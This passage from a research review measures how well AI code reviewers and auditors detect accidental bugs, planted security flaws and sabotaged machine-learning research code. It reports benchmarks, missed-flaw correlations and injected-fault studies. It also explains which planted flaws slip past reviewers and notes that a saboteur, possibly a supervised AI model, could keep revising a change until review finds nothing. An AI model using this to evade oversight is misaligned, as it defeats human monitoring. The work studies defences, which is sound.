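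In half of the open-source tasks, a human reviewer had pointed out the bug before the project accepted the change, so the researchers gave the agents the version the reviewer had commented on. The other bugs were found later, and the researchers had to work out which change had introduced them. They used a method called SZZ, which starts from the fix. If a fix replaces `<=` with `<` in the expiry check, SZZ finds the change that last touched that line and treats it as the source of the bug. But that change may have only renamed `expires`, so a language model checked 1,168 of the changes SZZ had identified and rejected more than a third of them. The researchers then examined 40 bugs from the finished collection and judged 37 to be real and detectable from the information available.

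SZZ looks for the commit that introduced a bug by tracing the lines that the fix changed or deleted, so it has nothing to trace when a fix only adds lines. Flaws that consist of missing code are often fixed this way, so they are probably scarce among the later-discovered bugs it identifies.

Each agent received the project's code, the diff, the title and the description, but no hint that there was a bug. It ranked its findings by severity, and three language models voted on whether any of them matched the known bug. These votes agreed almost perfectly with the researchers' own judgments on a sample of 40. The table gives results for the open-source tasks. The two recall columns count a bug as caught if it was among the agent's top five findings:

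| Model | Recall, bugs that human reviewers caught | Recall, bugs found later | First finding correct | Findings per review | Cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 79.6% | 64.2% | 42% | 6.3 | $2.97 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 70.0% | 46.6% | 39% | 2.8 | $1.76 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 65.6% | 49.0% | 37% | 3.1 | $1.77 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 63.9% | 47.8% | 37% | 3.1 | $0.62 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 59.1% | 36.4% | 36% | 2.3 | $1.22 |

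Opus 5 caught 71.9% of the bugs, counting both kinds, within its top five findings, compared with 47.7% for Opus 4.6, a model five months older. Much of this improvement comes from longer reviews. Opus 5 listed more than twice as many findings, but its first finding identified the bug only six percentage points more often.

Performance was up to 25.5% lower on the private repositories than on the open-source projects. Only 22.8% of the bugs in the private repositories were visible in the diff, compared with 46.1% in the open-source projects, but this explains just a fifth of the gap. The models may also have done better on the open-source projects because they had seen some of the fixes in training, which can't have happened with the private code. A company using an agent to review its own code should probably expect results closer to those from the private repositories.

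Pereira, Sinha and colleagues (2026) report much lower recall in *CR-Bench-v2*, where the best agents caught only about a third of 174 bugs in Python projects. Most of the difference seems to come from the models, since those agents ran on GPT-5.2 and GPT-5-mini, which are older or smaller. GPT-5-mini did about equally well on both benchmarks, catching 33.7% of the bugs in CR-Bench-v2 and 33.4% of the later-found bugs in CRBugBench.

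Pereira and colleagues also tested Gemini Code Assist, Google's commercial reviewer. Language models rated 78% of its comments as useful, but it caught only 8.1% of the known bugs. How often developers like or act on an agent's comments is therefore a poor measure of how many bugs the agent misses.

### What makes a bug harder to catch

Yang, He and colleagues used a regression to estimate how each property of a change or bug affects detection when the others stay the same. The results are odds ratios. If an agent has a 60% chance of catching a bug, the odds are 60 to 40, or 1.5. An odds ratio of 0.5 would halve them to 0.75, which is a 43% chance. The table applies the main results to that 60% starting point:

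| Difference | Odds ratio | A 60% chance becomes |
|---|---|---|
| The bug is not visible in the diff | 0.38 | 36% |
| The change is a bug fix, not a new feature | 0.52 | 44% |
| The diff is longer by one standard deviation (log scale) | 0.59 | 47% |
| The change includes one more type of file, such as tests | 0.80 | 54% |
| The bug is severe | 1.91 | 74% |

The programming language and the size of the repository had no clear effect. Some of these results could help a saboteur, who could put a flaw in a long bug fix that depends on code elsewhere. The result for severe bugs is more reassuring, because a flaw worth planting would usually be severe.

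The agents spent 75% of their steps reading and searching and only 8% running code, although running code can settle questions that reading leaves open. In one task from yt-dlp, a program for downloading videos, Opus 5 fetched about 25 archived web pages and ran the changed code on some of them. It found that the code worked on only two of the nine livestream pages it tried, a bug that other models missed.

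The six strongest models opened the faulty file in 95.6% of runs and reported something about it in 80.2%, but they identified the bug in only 56.2%. Sometimes they relied on the author's account of the code. In a task from Selenium, a tool for automating web browsers, every model approved a faulty condition because the comment and the description both stated what the code was supposed to do, which differed from what it did. In a task from the search engine Elasticsearch, Opus 5 used the faulty line as its example of correct code when checking the rest of the file.

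### The right file and the wrong explanation

In *Can Agentic Code Review Catch Vulnerabilities Before They Are Merged?*, Yang, Yang and colleagues (2026) looked only at security flaws. They built SecPRBench from 265 vulnerabilities in nine C, C++ or Rust projects, including Firefox, OpenSSL and V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine. In nearly all cases, the agents reviewed the change that had introduced the vulnerability. The agents had the commit message and the source code, and the researchers told them to look for security problems but not what the problem was.

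To make sure they had the right change, the researchers ran the same proof of concept on the program before the change, after it, and after it with the later repair added. The failure had to occur in the second version and in neither of the others. Automatic checks, mostly of this kind, settled 217 cases, and people decided the other 48 from the code and other evidence.

A finding counted only if it explained what triggers the flaw, which operation becomes unsafe and which safety condition the code violates. Claude Opus 5.5 judged the findings, although it was also one of the models tested. This seems to have mattered little, since only seven of its 265 verdicts on its own reviews differed from Claude Sonnet 4.6's.

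| Model | Recall, all flaws | Recall, memory flaws | Recall, logic errors | Misses with a wrong explanation in the right file | Cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.6 | 78.1% | 84.0% | 69.8% | 79% | $3.20 |
| GPT-6 Sol | 76.2% | 82.4% | 67.4% | 62% | $0.60 |
| GLM 5.3 | 74.7% | 85.6% | 62.8% | 93% | $4.99 |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 74.0% | 85.6% | 61.6% | 84% | $0.44 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 59.2% | 68.8% | 44.2% | 76% | $0.83 |
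| GPT-5.6 Sol | 55.8% | 69.6% | 43.0% | 54% | $0.74 |
| GPT-6 Luna | 55.5% | 68.8% | 44.2% | 56% | $0.02 |
| MiniMax M3 | 32.5% | 40.0% | 18.6% | 62% | $3.33 |

The top four are too close to rank with confidence. In 68% of the misses across all eight, the agent reported a problem in the right file but described a different mechanism.

A finding can be in the right place and still be wrong. In Wasmtime, which runs WebAssembly programs, a change made a function expect one kind of table number, but a caller outside the diff still passed another, so the program could access the wrong table. A generic warning about missing bounds checks on that call would not count as finding the flaw, because adding them would leave the mismatch in place. In the download tool curl, a nine-line change left a pointer to memory that the program had already released. All eight agents reported something in that file,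 but four said that the program never released the memory, and the three GPT models called the flaw a logic error.

A report that names the right file but gives the wrong explanation is very weak evidence that the agent noticed the flaw. When the agents reviewed versions of the same changes with the flaw repaired, they still reported something in the file where the flaw had been in 74.9% of reviews. By comparison, they correctly diagnosed 63.3% of the flaws that were present. Nor does a developer need such a report to find the file, since the diff already shows it. The report could even do harm if the developer checks the wrong explanation, finds that it doesn't hold and accepts the change.

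Average recall was lower for logic errors (51.5%) than for memory flaws (73.1%). About a third of the logic errors came from V8, where recall was low in general, but every model also did worse on logic errors in the other projects. Planted logic errors like the one in the expiry check are therefore likely to be hard to find.

Recall also fell when understanding the flaw required several files, from 69.6% for one file to 38.5% for five or more. Larger changes don't fully explain the drop, because among changes to two to five files, recall was 76.5% when one file was enough to understand the flaw and 55.1% when more were needed.

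### Why eight reviewers miss the same flaws

Adding more agents helps less than their individual miss rates suggest, because the agents tend to miss the same flaws. If their misses were independent, the share of flaws that all of them miss would be the product of their miss rates. For Grok 4.6, GPT-6 Sol and GLM 5.3, that product is 0.219 × 0.238 × 0.253 = 0.013, or 3.5 of the 265 flaws, but 27 flaws got past all three. For all eight agents, the product is 0.00019, or 0.05 flaws, but 23 got past all eight.

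Most of the benefit came from the first few agents. Grok 4.6 missed 58 flaws on its own. GPT-6 Sol and GLM 5.3 found 31 of those, and the other five agents together found only four more.

A simple model fits these numbers fairly well: no agent can find 23 of the flaws, and misses on the other 242 are independent. The three leading agents would then together miss about 24 flaws, close to the 27 they actually missed. In this model, the first few reviewers find nearly every flaw that can be found, so adding more helps little.

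It is unclear why the agents missed the same flaws. Yang, Yang and colleagues suggest that these flaws may be difficult, that the models may have learned from the same data, or that the grading may have been too strict or mistaken. If the grading was at fault, the agents performed better than their scores indicate. At least four of them still reported some other problem in nearly all of the 23 changes.

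Language models share mistakes on other tasks too. Kohli (2026), in *Nine Judges, Two Effective Votes*, had nine models judge how pairs of sentences relate, for instance whether one follows from the other. All nine were wrong on 51 of 1,000 items, when independent errors would have produced fewer than one such item. The number of independent votes that k models are worth is roughly

```
k / (1 + (k − 1) × c)
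```

where c is the average correlation between two models' errors. With nine models and a correlation of 0.391, the result is 2.2. Even an unlimited number of models with that correlation would be worth only 1/0.391, or 2.6 votes.

Correlations between pairs of models can still understate how often all of them fail together. Chen (2026), in *When Does Combining Language Models Help?*, tested 67 models on mathematics problems, and all of them failed on 5.2% of the problems. The estimate from pairwise correlations was just over 2%. Measuring what a panel of reviewers would miss therefore requires testing the whole panel on known flaws and counting the ones that no reviewer finds.

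Choosing models from different developers should help somewhat, because *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) found that models from the same developer make more strongly correlated errors. However, CRBugBench did not show this gain. Combining three reviews by GPT-5.6 Sol raised its recall by 3.5 percentage points, compared with 2.5 points for combining reviews by GPT-5.6 Sol, GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8. Both combinations cost about three and a half times as much as a single review. Asking GPT-5.6 Sol for a more comprehensive list raised recall by 5.3 points at no extra cost.

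Changing a model's review process can uncover flaws that switching models doesn't. Yang, Yang and colleagues also ran Opus 5.5 in Anthropic's Defending Code harness, a program that takes the model through a longer security review. On the 260 tasks it completed, recall rose from 73.8% to 81.5%. It found six of the 23 flaws that all eight agents had missed. The reviews cost about ten times as much, and the six successful reports contained 14–32 findings each, so part of the success may come from making more guesses. OpenAI's Codex Security, however, lowered GPT-5.6 Sol's recall by 8.3 points, mainly because it more often reported nothing.

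Some evidence also weighs against letting a model review its own work. Trębacz and colleagues report that OpenAI's reviewer found a smaller share of known issues in code written by its own underlying model than in code written by people. Shared blind spots could explain this, but so could a difference in the kinds of mistakes people and models make.

Human and AI reviewers miss different problems. Opus 5 caught 64.2% of the CRBugBench bugs that had escaped human review, but missed 20.4% of those that people had caught. Agents were better than people at spotting severe bugs, but worse at spotting code that would be hard to maintain.

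### Flaws that nobody has found

All of these benchmarks consist of accidental flaws that people later found and fixed, which probably makes the agents look better than they are. Suppose a set of changes contains 100 flaws and people eventually find 80 of them. An agent that catches 75% of those 80, but only 25% of the 20 they miss, has a measured recall of 75% and a true recall of 65%. Nobody knows the real numbers, because a flaw can't enter a benchmark until somebody has found it.

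The people who made these mistakes also weren't trying to get them past a reviewer. Even the comment that misled every model in the Selenium task was written in good faith. Someone planting a flaw could run the review agent in advance and keep revising the change until it reports no problems.

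## Searching for flaws planted on purpose

The bugs in the previous section were accidental. In several experiments from 2026, researchers created flaws deliberately, or treated existing ones as if somebody had planted them, and measured whether reviewers could find them. Some flaws weaken the security of ordinary software. Others spoil the results of machine learning experiments, where code can run without errors and still lead to a false conclusion.

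### Changes with a missing protection

Chen, Wang and colleagues (2026) introduce MalPR-Bench in *From Verdict to Diagnosis*. It contains 50 benign controls and 89 pull requests that they treat as malicious.

The researchers made 44 of the 89 from fixes for publicly disclosed vulnerabilities. In 37 of these, the change deletes a protection, so a reviewer can see the deletion in the diff. The other seven contain a real fix with one necessary check left out, so the reviewer has to notice that the check is missing. Another 33 come from project histories in which developers had fixed a vulnerability but left a related route open until a later patch. The last 12 are previously undisclosed vulnerabilities that the researchers' own review system, PRGuard, found in five widely used projects. Each benign control contains a complete fix.

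About half of the flaws are natural bugs, and the rest are injected faults, which the researchers selected by fixed criteria before running any reviewer. Nobody designed the injected faults to be hard to spot, so they may be easier to find than real sabotage. Misleading descriptions can also lower detection, as *When AI Agrees Too Much* (2026) found for automated reviewers.

### Blocking a change for the wrong reason

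Suppose a pull request adds a function that accepts access tokens but never checks whether the owner has revoked them. An older function in the same project does make that check. Chen and colleagues would give a review of this change three separate scores:

- The review passes on verdict if it blocks the change.
- It passes on identification if it explains that the new function accepts revoked tokens because a check is missing, and what an attacker could do as a result.
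- It passes on evidence if it also points to the code that proves this, such as the unprotected line and the older function that makes the check.

A review that blocks the change because the token might end up in a log file reaches the right verdict but misses the planted flaw. The author could fix the logging and resubmit, and revoked tokens would still work.

Something similar happened with one of the 12 newly discovered vulnerabilities. A change to an automation platform let users resume a saved run by sending its ID, but existing code looked up the run without checking that it belonged to the user's project. Anyone with a valid ID could resume another project's run and see its stored conversation. CodeRabbit, a widely used commercial reviewer, blocked the change, but because of an unrelated problem with how secrets were displayed.

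Because of CodeRabbit's cost and usage limits, the researchers ran it on only 31 of the flaws. They compared it with PRGuard running on DeepSeek v4-pro, an open-weight model:

| Flaws | CodeRabbit blocked | CodeRabbit identified | PRGuard blocked | PRGuard identified |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Omission flaws (14) | 9 | 3 | 9 | 9 |
| Other flaws (17) | 15 | 13 | 13 | 13 |
| All (31) | 24 | 16 | 22 | 22 |

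Eight of CodeRabbit's blocks, a third of the total, were for the wrong reason, and six of those involved omission flaws. CodeRabbit usually explained the flaw correctly when the code contained something visibly wrong, but it often flagged something else when a check was missing.

CodeRabbit identified 16 of the 24 flaws that a reviewer could establish from the changed files alone, but none of the seven that required looking at other files. CodeQL, a conventional tool that searches code for known patterns of error, identified none of the flaws. Its standard security rules applied to 21 of the 31 cases.

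PRGuard's advantage is less secure than the table suggests, because 12 of the 31 cases were ones PRGuard itself had discovered, using a different model. On those 12, PRGuard with DeepSeek identified ten flaws and CodeRabbit four. On the other 19, each identified 12, but CodeRabbit backed its blocks with the right explanation and evidence for 12 flaws, compared with PRGuard's nine. The whole difference in identification therefore comes from the 12 cases that favored PRGuard, which also include nine of the 14 omission flaws.

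This bias affects how common CodeRabbit's wrong explanations appear. CodeRabbit blocked 14 of the 19 other cases and identified the flaw in 12. It blocked ten of PRGuard's 12 discoveries and identified the flaw in four. PRGuard's discoveries were mostly omission flaws and had all gone unnoticed in real projects, so they may be a better guide to well-hidden flaws than the 19 that developers had already found.

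Blocking a change for the wrong reason is still useful if somebody then discards the change or examines all of it again. But if the author only has to repair the reported problem, the planted flaw survives the review.

### How PRGuard looks for missing code

PRGuard doesn't go straight from a diff to a verdict. It first gathers related code, then proposes possible flaws, and then tries to prove or disprove each one. It never runs the code under review. In the example with revoked tokens, it would work like this:

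1. An ordinary program, without a language model, collects code connected to the change. This includes functions that call the new one, code that uses the same data, and other functions that perform the same sensitive operation. It should find the older function that checks for revoked tokens. Because this happens first, a language model's early guess can't limit what the later steps see.
2. A language model describes what the change does to the program's security, without suggesting a flaw. It marks anything the code doesn't settle as unknown.
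3. PRGuard compares this description with 21 stored flaw mechanisms and uses up to three of the closest matches to guide the review. Some of them lead it to fetch more code, such as functions with a similar role that ought to have the same protection. It also lists places to check based only on the change, in case none of the stored mechanisms fits.
4. The model proposes specific flaws, such as "the new function accepts revoked tokens." For each, it states what an attacker needs to control, how the attack would work, and what evidence is still missing.
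5. In a separate call, the model tests each proposal against the code. Here it would have to confirm that no other function rejects the revoked token first. It can request a few more definitions before it accepts the proposal, marks it as unproven or rejects it.
6. A fixed rule blocks the change if the model accepted any proposal, leaves a comment if it marked one as unproven, and otherwise approves. The model then writes the review but can't change the verdict.

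The stored mechanisms came from 14 of the 33 flaws taken from project histories, so the researchers left those 14 out of the results. They also left out PRGuard's own 12 discoveries when they tested the system with two models. In each pair of numbers below, the first is for GPT-5.5 and the second for DeepSeek:

| Origin of the flaw | Flaws | Identified | Blocked with correct explanation and evidence | Controls wrongly blocked |
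|---|---|---|---|---|
| Developers' fix was incomplete | 19 | 14 / 12 | 12 / 9 | 0 / 0 of 6 |
| Researchers left a check out of a fix | 7 | 3 / 3 | 3 / 2 | 2 / 1 of 7 |
| Researchers deleted a protection | 37 | 37 / 37 | 26 / 33 | 3 / 3 of 37 |
| Total | 63 | 54 / 52 | 41 / 44 | 5 / 4 of 50 |

The totals look good mainly because more than half of the flaws are deletions visible in the diff. PRGuard identified all of those, but only three of the seven flaws in which researchers had left out a check. These seven are closer to what a model could do when writing a new function, because it has no existing protection to delete but could leave out a check. But seven cases are too few for a reliable rate.

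GPT-5.5 had the opposite problem from CodeRabbit. It identified all 37 deleted protections but blocked only 26 of the changes. Anyone who looked only at the verdicts would have missed 11 correct reports.

GPT-5.5 raised false alarms on 10% of the controls and DeepSeek on 8%. The controls are complete security fixes, which probably invite more suspicion than ordinary changes. In the small group with a missing check, GPT-5.5 blocked four of the seven flawed changes and two of the seven complete fixes, so its alarms were weak evidence of a flaw.

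Related code helps with omission flaws. When the researchers gave the models only the diff for 12 of these flaws, GPT-5.5 blocked one change, for the wrong reason, and DeepSeek blocked none. With the full system, GPT-5.5 blocked six and DeepSeek blocked five. On the 19 flaws from incomplete fixes, the full system mostly improved the evidence in the reviews. The number of reviews with sufficient evidence rose from 6 to 12 with GPT-5.5 and from 6 to 10 with DeepSeek, while the number of flaws identified rose by only one or two. The full system differs from the diff-only version in several ways, so these experiments can't show which part helped.

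An agent may miss a planted flaw even when it can search the whole repository. Chen and colleagues gave a Codex agent that access and ran it twice on each of seven flawed changes. For four of them, the evidence was elsewhere in the changed files, and the agent identified three of those flaws. For the other three, finding the flaw depended on comparing the changed code with a function that had a similar role but no direct connection to it. The agent blocked the change in four of those six runs but never identified the flaw. The researchers chose these cases deliberately, so the result doesn't show how common the difficulty is. The result is consistent with the drop in recall on accidental vulnerabilities whose explanation involves several files.

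Reviews also vary between runs. When the researchers repeated PRGuard's reviews of 44 flawed changes, the decision on whether to block differed in 25% of cases with DeepSeek and 18% with GPT-5.5. Whether the review identified the flaw changed in only 7% and 5% of cases, respectively. A typical review takes less than three minutes, so a second one adds little time.

The 12 discoveries give some idea of how PRGuard performs when nobody has chosen a flaw for it to find. The researchers collected about 890 past changes and used a language model to filter them to about 80 that looked worth investigating. PRGuard blocked 19 of those. Manual checks of the source code confirmed 14 of the reports, and the researchers produced a working proof of concept for 12. At least 12 of 19 is a good yield for a security tool, but the filtering helped, and nobody knows how many flaws PRGuard missed.

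### Running the changed program

A tool that runs the changed code can sometimes avoid giving a wrong explanation, because it has an input that triggers the flaw. Lily, presented in *Not In My Git Yard* (Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli, 2026), takes this approach and builds on ideas from ROSA, the fuzzing tool described earlier that looks for backdoors.

Lily fuzzes the new version of a program for ten minutes and records the types of system calls that each input causes. It reports an input only if the combination of calls does not occur when the new version runs a set of inputs saved from earlier fuzzing, and the old version does not make the same combination on that input. Lily then points to the changed lines that ran on that input and the lines that led to the unusual calls.

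The researchers planted backdoors in 13 open-source programs, including copies of three backdoors from real attacks. Lily detected them in 90% of 260 runs on single changes and 83% of 1,000 runs on whole releases. It raised false alarms in 0.2% of 8,640 runs on legitimate changes and 4.3% of runs on legitimate releases. Most of the false alarms on single changes came from very large merges in PHP.

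Lily also gave precise locations. A release of the file server vsFTPd that contained a real backdoor differed from the previous release by 1,407 lines in five files. Lily narrowed this to seven lines in one file, in which the program opens a network connection and hands control to whoever connects. Across the experiments, it left a reviewer with fewer than a dozen lines to read.

Lily has a far lower false alarm rate than PRGuard on single changes, but it can only find flaws that change how the program interacts with the operating system. It also needs an older version of the program and a way to fuzz it. Like ROSA, Lily would probably miss a flaw in a token check, which PRGuard might find. It makes sense to use both Lily and PRGuard on an important change.

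### Research code that produces a false result

A saboteur may be able to mislead researchers just by making a safety method look useless or a useless one look effective, without opening a way into a computer. In April 2026, Redwood Research, which studies AI control, released Auditing Sabotage Bench (ASMR-Bench) to test whether auditors can detect this kind of sabotage in machine learning code.

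The benchmark uses nine research projects from published papers. For each one, a researcher prepared an honest version of the code that reproduces a key finding, then made one or two sabotaged versions (11 in total) that change the finding. The sabotage alters implementation details but keeps the general method described in the paper.

One project concerns subliminal learning, in which a language model told to like owls passes this preference to another model through training data made up only of number sequences. The sabotaged version uses four different animals and cuts the training data from 10,000 samples to 1,000. Either change could pass for an ordinary research decision, but the effect disappears, so the experiment appears to show that subliminal learning doesn't work.

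An auditor receives a paper and its code and knows there is a 50% chance of sabotage. The auditor then gives a probability that the code has been sabotaged, which measures detection, and a ranked list of five possible fixes, which measures diagnosis.

The detection score is the AUROC (area under the receiver operating characteristic curve). It is the chance that a randomly chosen sabotaged project gets a higher probability of sabotage than a randomly chosen honest one, with ties counting as half. Suppose an auditor gives three sabotaged projects 80%, 60% and 30%, and two honest ones 50% and 20%. The sabotaged project gets the higher probability in five of the six possible pairs, so the AUROC is 5/6, or 0.83. Guessing gives 0.5 on average, and a perfect auditor scores 1. The AUROC depends only on the order of the probabilities, so an auditor can score well even if the probabilities it gives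 are all far too high.

The best auditor, Gemini 3.1 Pro, could also run experiments and had an AUROC of 0.77. Its first suggested fix was right for 42% of the sabotaged projects, and one of its five suggestions was right for 53%. *AI Safety at the Frontier Paper Highlights of April 2026* (2026) reports that 31 people also audited projects with help from language models. They had two hours per project and could read an audit by GPT-5.2. Their AUROC was 0.68. Their first suggested fix was right in 38% of cases, and one of their five suggestions was right in 54%. Several said that two hours was short and that they had relied heavily on the models to understand the code.

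Results varied widely by kind of sabotage. When the sabotage was an outright error in code or mathematics, one of Gemini 3.1 Pro's five suggestions almost always identified it. The model did much worse with poor choices of settings, prompts or data. For four of the sabotaged projects, all of this second kind, no auditor included the right fix more than 20% of the time. The researchers concluded that the hardest sabotage to detect is an important choice that the paper never mentions. This resembles an omission flaw, but the omission is in the paper, and the code may be complete.

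Real research projects contain bugs, strange leftovers and questionable decisions, and auditors often mistook these for sabotage, which caused many of the false alarms. These flaws raised the probability of sabotage that auditors gave to unsabotaged projects and took up places on the list of fixes. Gemini 3.1 Pro, GPT-5.2 and the human auditors all overestimated the probability of sabotage, putting it above 50% for most projects.

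Claude Opus 4.6 made the opposite mistake, tending to accept oddities as reasonable decisions. It gave most projects a less than 50% chance of being sabotaged, sometimes even when its list included the correct fix. People also differed in how readily they suspected sabotage. This lowered their combined AUROC, because a cautious auditor's 40% could mean the same as a suspicious auditor's 70%.

The Redwood researchers also asked language models to create sabotage. The best AUROC for sabotage by Claude Opus 4.6 was 0.80, about the same as for human sabotage. But the model's flaws were easier to diagnose, and the right fix came first in up to 68% of cases. Opus 4.6 is no longer among the strongest models, so a current one might hide its changes better.

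### What made the two tasks different

A reviewer in MalPR-Bench starts with a diff, which narrows the search to a small amount of code. The reviewer also has a fairly clear standard of correctness. If every other function that accepts tokens checks for revocation, a new one that doesn't is probably wrong. An auditor in ASMR-Bench gets a paper and a complete codebase, with no unsabotaged version to compare it with. Whether 1,000 training samples are too few depends on the experiment, and reading the code may not be enough to tell.

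The flaws were also chosen differently. Most flaws in MalPR-Bench are based on what developers had repaired, whether or not the flaws were easy to notice. In ASMR-Bench, one person tried to make each change look innocent and could rerun the experiment until a change altered the finding. Many attempts failed because small changes often make little difference to a machine learning result. A supervised AI model might not be able to make so many attempts without drawing attention.

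This makes ASMR-Bench closer to sabotage in one respect, because someone was trying to deceive the auditor. But its auditors had advantages they might lack in practice. They knew that about half of the projects contained sabotage. The papers were also public, and *AI Safety at the Frontier Paper Highlights of April 2026* warns that models probably remembered some of the correct findings.

The two benchmarks are most comparable on how often a reviewer identified the real flaw. Excluding the 37 deleted protections, PRGuard identified 17 of 26 flaws with GPT-5.5 and 15 with DeepSeek, or about 60%. In ASMR-Bench, the best auditor's five suggestions included the right fix 53% of the time. The small gap between these figures means little because the models and grading rules differed, but a large share of the flaws went undiagnosed in both benchmarks.

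### Auditing research with no published answer

*Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research* (Shenoy, Zang and colleagues, 2026) describes a later experiment that used ten new research questions, so no one had the advantage of knowing the published result. One experienced researcher answered each question as well as possible, then repeated nine of the projects while trying to reach a false conclusion without getting caught. The result was ten honest projects and twelve sabotaged ones. The researcher could interfere with the experimental design, the code or the final report, so only some of the sabotage is in the code.

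The 25 human auditors performed 104 audits. For each, they had 90 minutes, the logged history of the files and commands, and two audits by Claude Opus 4.8. They could also use other AI models and run experiments with no limit on computing costs. Their AUROC was 0.59, with a 95% interval from 0.37 to 0.77, so they may have done no better than guessing. The sabotaged projects contained 33 separate flaws. Counting each flaw once for every auditor who could have found it, the auditors fully identified 17%, partly identified 9% and missed the rest.

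Newer models working alone probably did better, even though they couldn't run experiments:

| Auditor | AUROC | Flaws fully identified |
|---|---|---|
| People assisted by models | 0.59 | 17% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 0.74 | 26% |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 0.73 | 32% |

The advantage over people could still be chance, since there were only ten research questions, but it fits an older result. In *LLM Critics Help Catch LLM Bugs (2024)*, language models caught many more of the bugs inserted into code than human contractors did. Those contractors were not the best reviewers available and often lacked knowledge of the subject.

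Several audits of the same project were better than one, because auditors found different flaws. If partial answers count as half, an average human audit scored 22%, and combining the best answers from the three to six audits of each project raised this to 47%. Reaching 47% in practice would require someone to tell which of the conflicting answers are right. Even combined, the reports from all the people and models did not fully diagnose 13 of the 33 flaws.

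Some auditors found a flaw but didn't flag the project as sabotaged. In one project, the saboteur avoided the method that had worked in the honest experiment and then reported that the effect didn't exist. One of three auditors identified this problem, but all three thought the project was more likely honest than sabotaged. That auditor may have taken the flaw for a poor decision that an honest researcher could also make. For safety purposes, the auditor's diagnosis would have been more useful than the verdict, because a reader could see from it what to change.

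The verdicts would be even less useful where sabotage is rare. When Shenoy and colleagues counted every probability of 50% or more as an alarm, 55% of audits of sabotaged projects and 35% of audits of honest ones produced alarms. At the same rates, if 100 of 10,000 projects were sabotaged, the auditors would flag about 55 of them along with more than 3,400 honest projects, so only 1.6% of the alarms would be real.

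Finding one flaw didn't lead auditors to the others in the same project. One sabotaged project had three major flaws, each serious enough to distort the conclusion unless corrected. Four of the five auditors fully identified one of these flaws and the fifth partly identified it, but none of them found the other two.

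## Whether results on injected faults carry over

Planted flaws are laborious to study because somebody has to make each one by hand. The two experiments on sabotaged research had only 11 and 12 sabotaged projects. An automatic tool can inject thousands of faults into working programs and record where it put them, which makes it easier to test a search method, but the results may not carry over to planted flaws.

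It is doubtful that results on injected faults carry over to planted flaws, because flaws get into a test set in different ways. An injected fault is included because a rule produced it and, usually, because at least one test fails on it. A natural bug is included because somebody noticed it, whereas whoever planted a flaw expected nobody to notice it.

### The same techniques on injected faults and natural bugs

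The most direct comparison of injected faults and natural bugs is in *Evaluating and improving fault localization* (Pearson, Campos and colleagues, 2017). The researchers took the repaired programs in Defects4J and used a tool to make small edits, such as swapping an operator, to the statements that developers had changed to fix the bugs. This produced 2,995 injected faults to compare with 310 natural bugs in the same places, using the same developer-written tests.

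The researchers ran seven localization techniques on both sets. Five use coverage: Tarantula, Ochiai, DStar, and two similar formulas, Barinel and Op2. The other two are the mutation techniques Metallaxis and MUSE. Earlier papers, which relied largely on artificial faults, had made ten claims that one of these techniques was better than another. Seven of the ten held on the injected faults, though only three of those seven differences were more than negligible. None held on the natural bugs. In four cases the technique claimed to be worse was significantly better, and in the other six there was no significant difference.

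The table gives the average EXAM scores, where lower is better:

| Technique | Evidence | Injected faults | Natural bugs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Metallaxis | Mutation | 0.043 | 0.075 |
| Op2 | Coverage | 0.050 | 0.048 |
| DStar | Coverage | 0.051 | 0.040 |
| Ochiai | Coverage | 0.051 | 0.041 |
| Barinel | Coverage | 0.056 | 0.042 |
| Tarantula | Coverage | 0.057 | 0.043 |
| MUSE | Mutation | 0.078 | 0.206 |

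Mutation techniques have an unfair advantage on injected faults because they search with the same kinds of edits that created the faults. If a tool injects a fault by changing `a + b` to `a - b`, one of the edits that Metallaxis and MUSE try will change it back and make every failing test pass. Almost none of the natural bugs had a repair that simple, and about 10% of them involved a statement that the mutation tool couldn't edit, for instance because deleting a `return` would stop the program from compiling. The mutation techniques don't rank such statements, so the researchers put them at the end of the list.

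These very low rankings account for much of Metallaxis's poor average. Compared with Ochiai bug by bug, Metallaxis gave the better ranking for 168 natural bugs and the worse one for 124. On the injected faults, its ranking was better for 1,900 and worse for 867. Metallaxis is therefore still useful on natural bugs, but the results on injected faults exaggerated its advantage and did not reveal its worst failures.

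The fault in the expiry check is reversible, since changing `<=` to `<` repairs it. The perfect score that Metallaxis gave it is typical of injected faults and would be unusual for a natural bug.

Tuning a tool on injected faults alone can also lead its designer to reject a change that helps on natural bugs. Pearson and colleagues found that MUSE did worse on reversible faults but much better on natural bugs when it counted edits that make a test fail in a different way, as well as edits that make it pass.

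The coverage techniques did slightly better on natural bugs than on injected faults. One likely reason is that 76% of real fixes change several statements, and a ranking got credit for finding any of them. When the ranking had to include every faulty statement, the best average EXAM score for any technique worsened from 0.040 to 0.191. Tests on single-edit faults can't show this difference, but it matters for a planted flaw spread over several statements that each look harmless alone.

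The results still disagreed when the comparison included only natural bugs on a single line. Each technique's performance on a natural bug correlated at best moderately with its performance on the faults injected in the same place. *Evaluating & improving fault localization techniques* (2016), an extended version of the study with 3,242 injected faults and 323 natural bugs, reached the same conclusions.

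This is a reason to be cautious about current language models' near-perfect results on one-line faults in short programs. A model that reads code doesn't benefit from reversible edits as MUSE does, but the experiment behind those results included no natural bugs, so it doesn't show whether the accuracy carries over to them.

### Whether tests that catch mutants catch natural bugs

Injected faults are a better guide to the quality of a test suite. *Are Mutants a Valid Substitute for Real Faults in Software Testing?* (Just, Jalali and colleagues, 2014) studied 357 natural bugs in five Java programs. For each bug, it compared a set of tests that missed the bug with the same set plus one test that exposed it. If mutants (injected faults) are good substitutes for natural bugs, the extra test should also catch mutants that the other tests missed.

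It did so for 73% of the bugs. For another 10%, the researchers judged that better or additional types of edit would have produced a suitable mutant, and for the remaining 17% they saw no practical type of edit that would. The link was also weaker when the extra test ran no new lines. Such tests caught two more mutants on average, and 40% of them caught no additional ones.

The researchers then generated about 35,000 test suites automatically. For 194 bugs, some suites caught the bug and others missed it. For 182 of these, the suites that caught the bug also caught significantly more mutants, even when the comparison covered only code that both suites ran. Adding tests until they catch most mutants is therefore a sensible way to prepare for natural bugs.

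This doesn't contradict the results of Pearson and colleagues. A thorough test can catch a wrong result whatever caused it, but how well a localization technique works depends more on the form of the fault, especially if the technique searches by trying edits.

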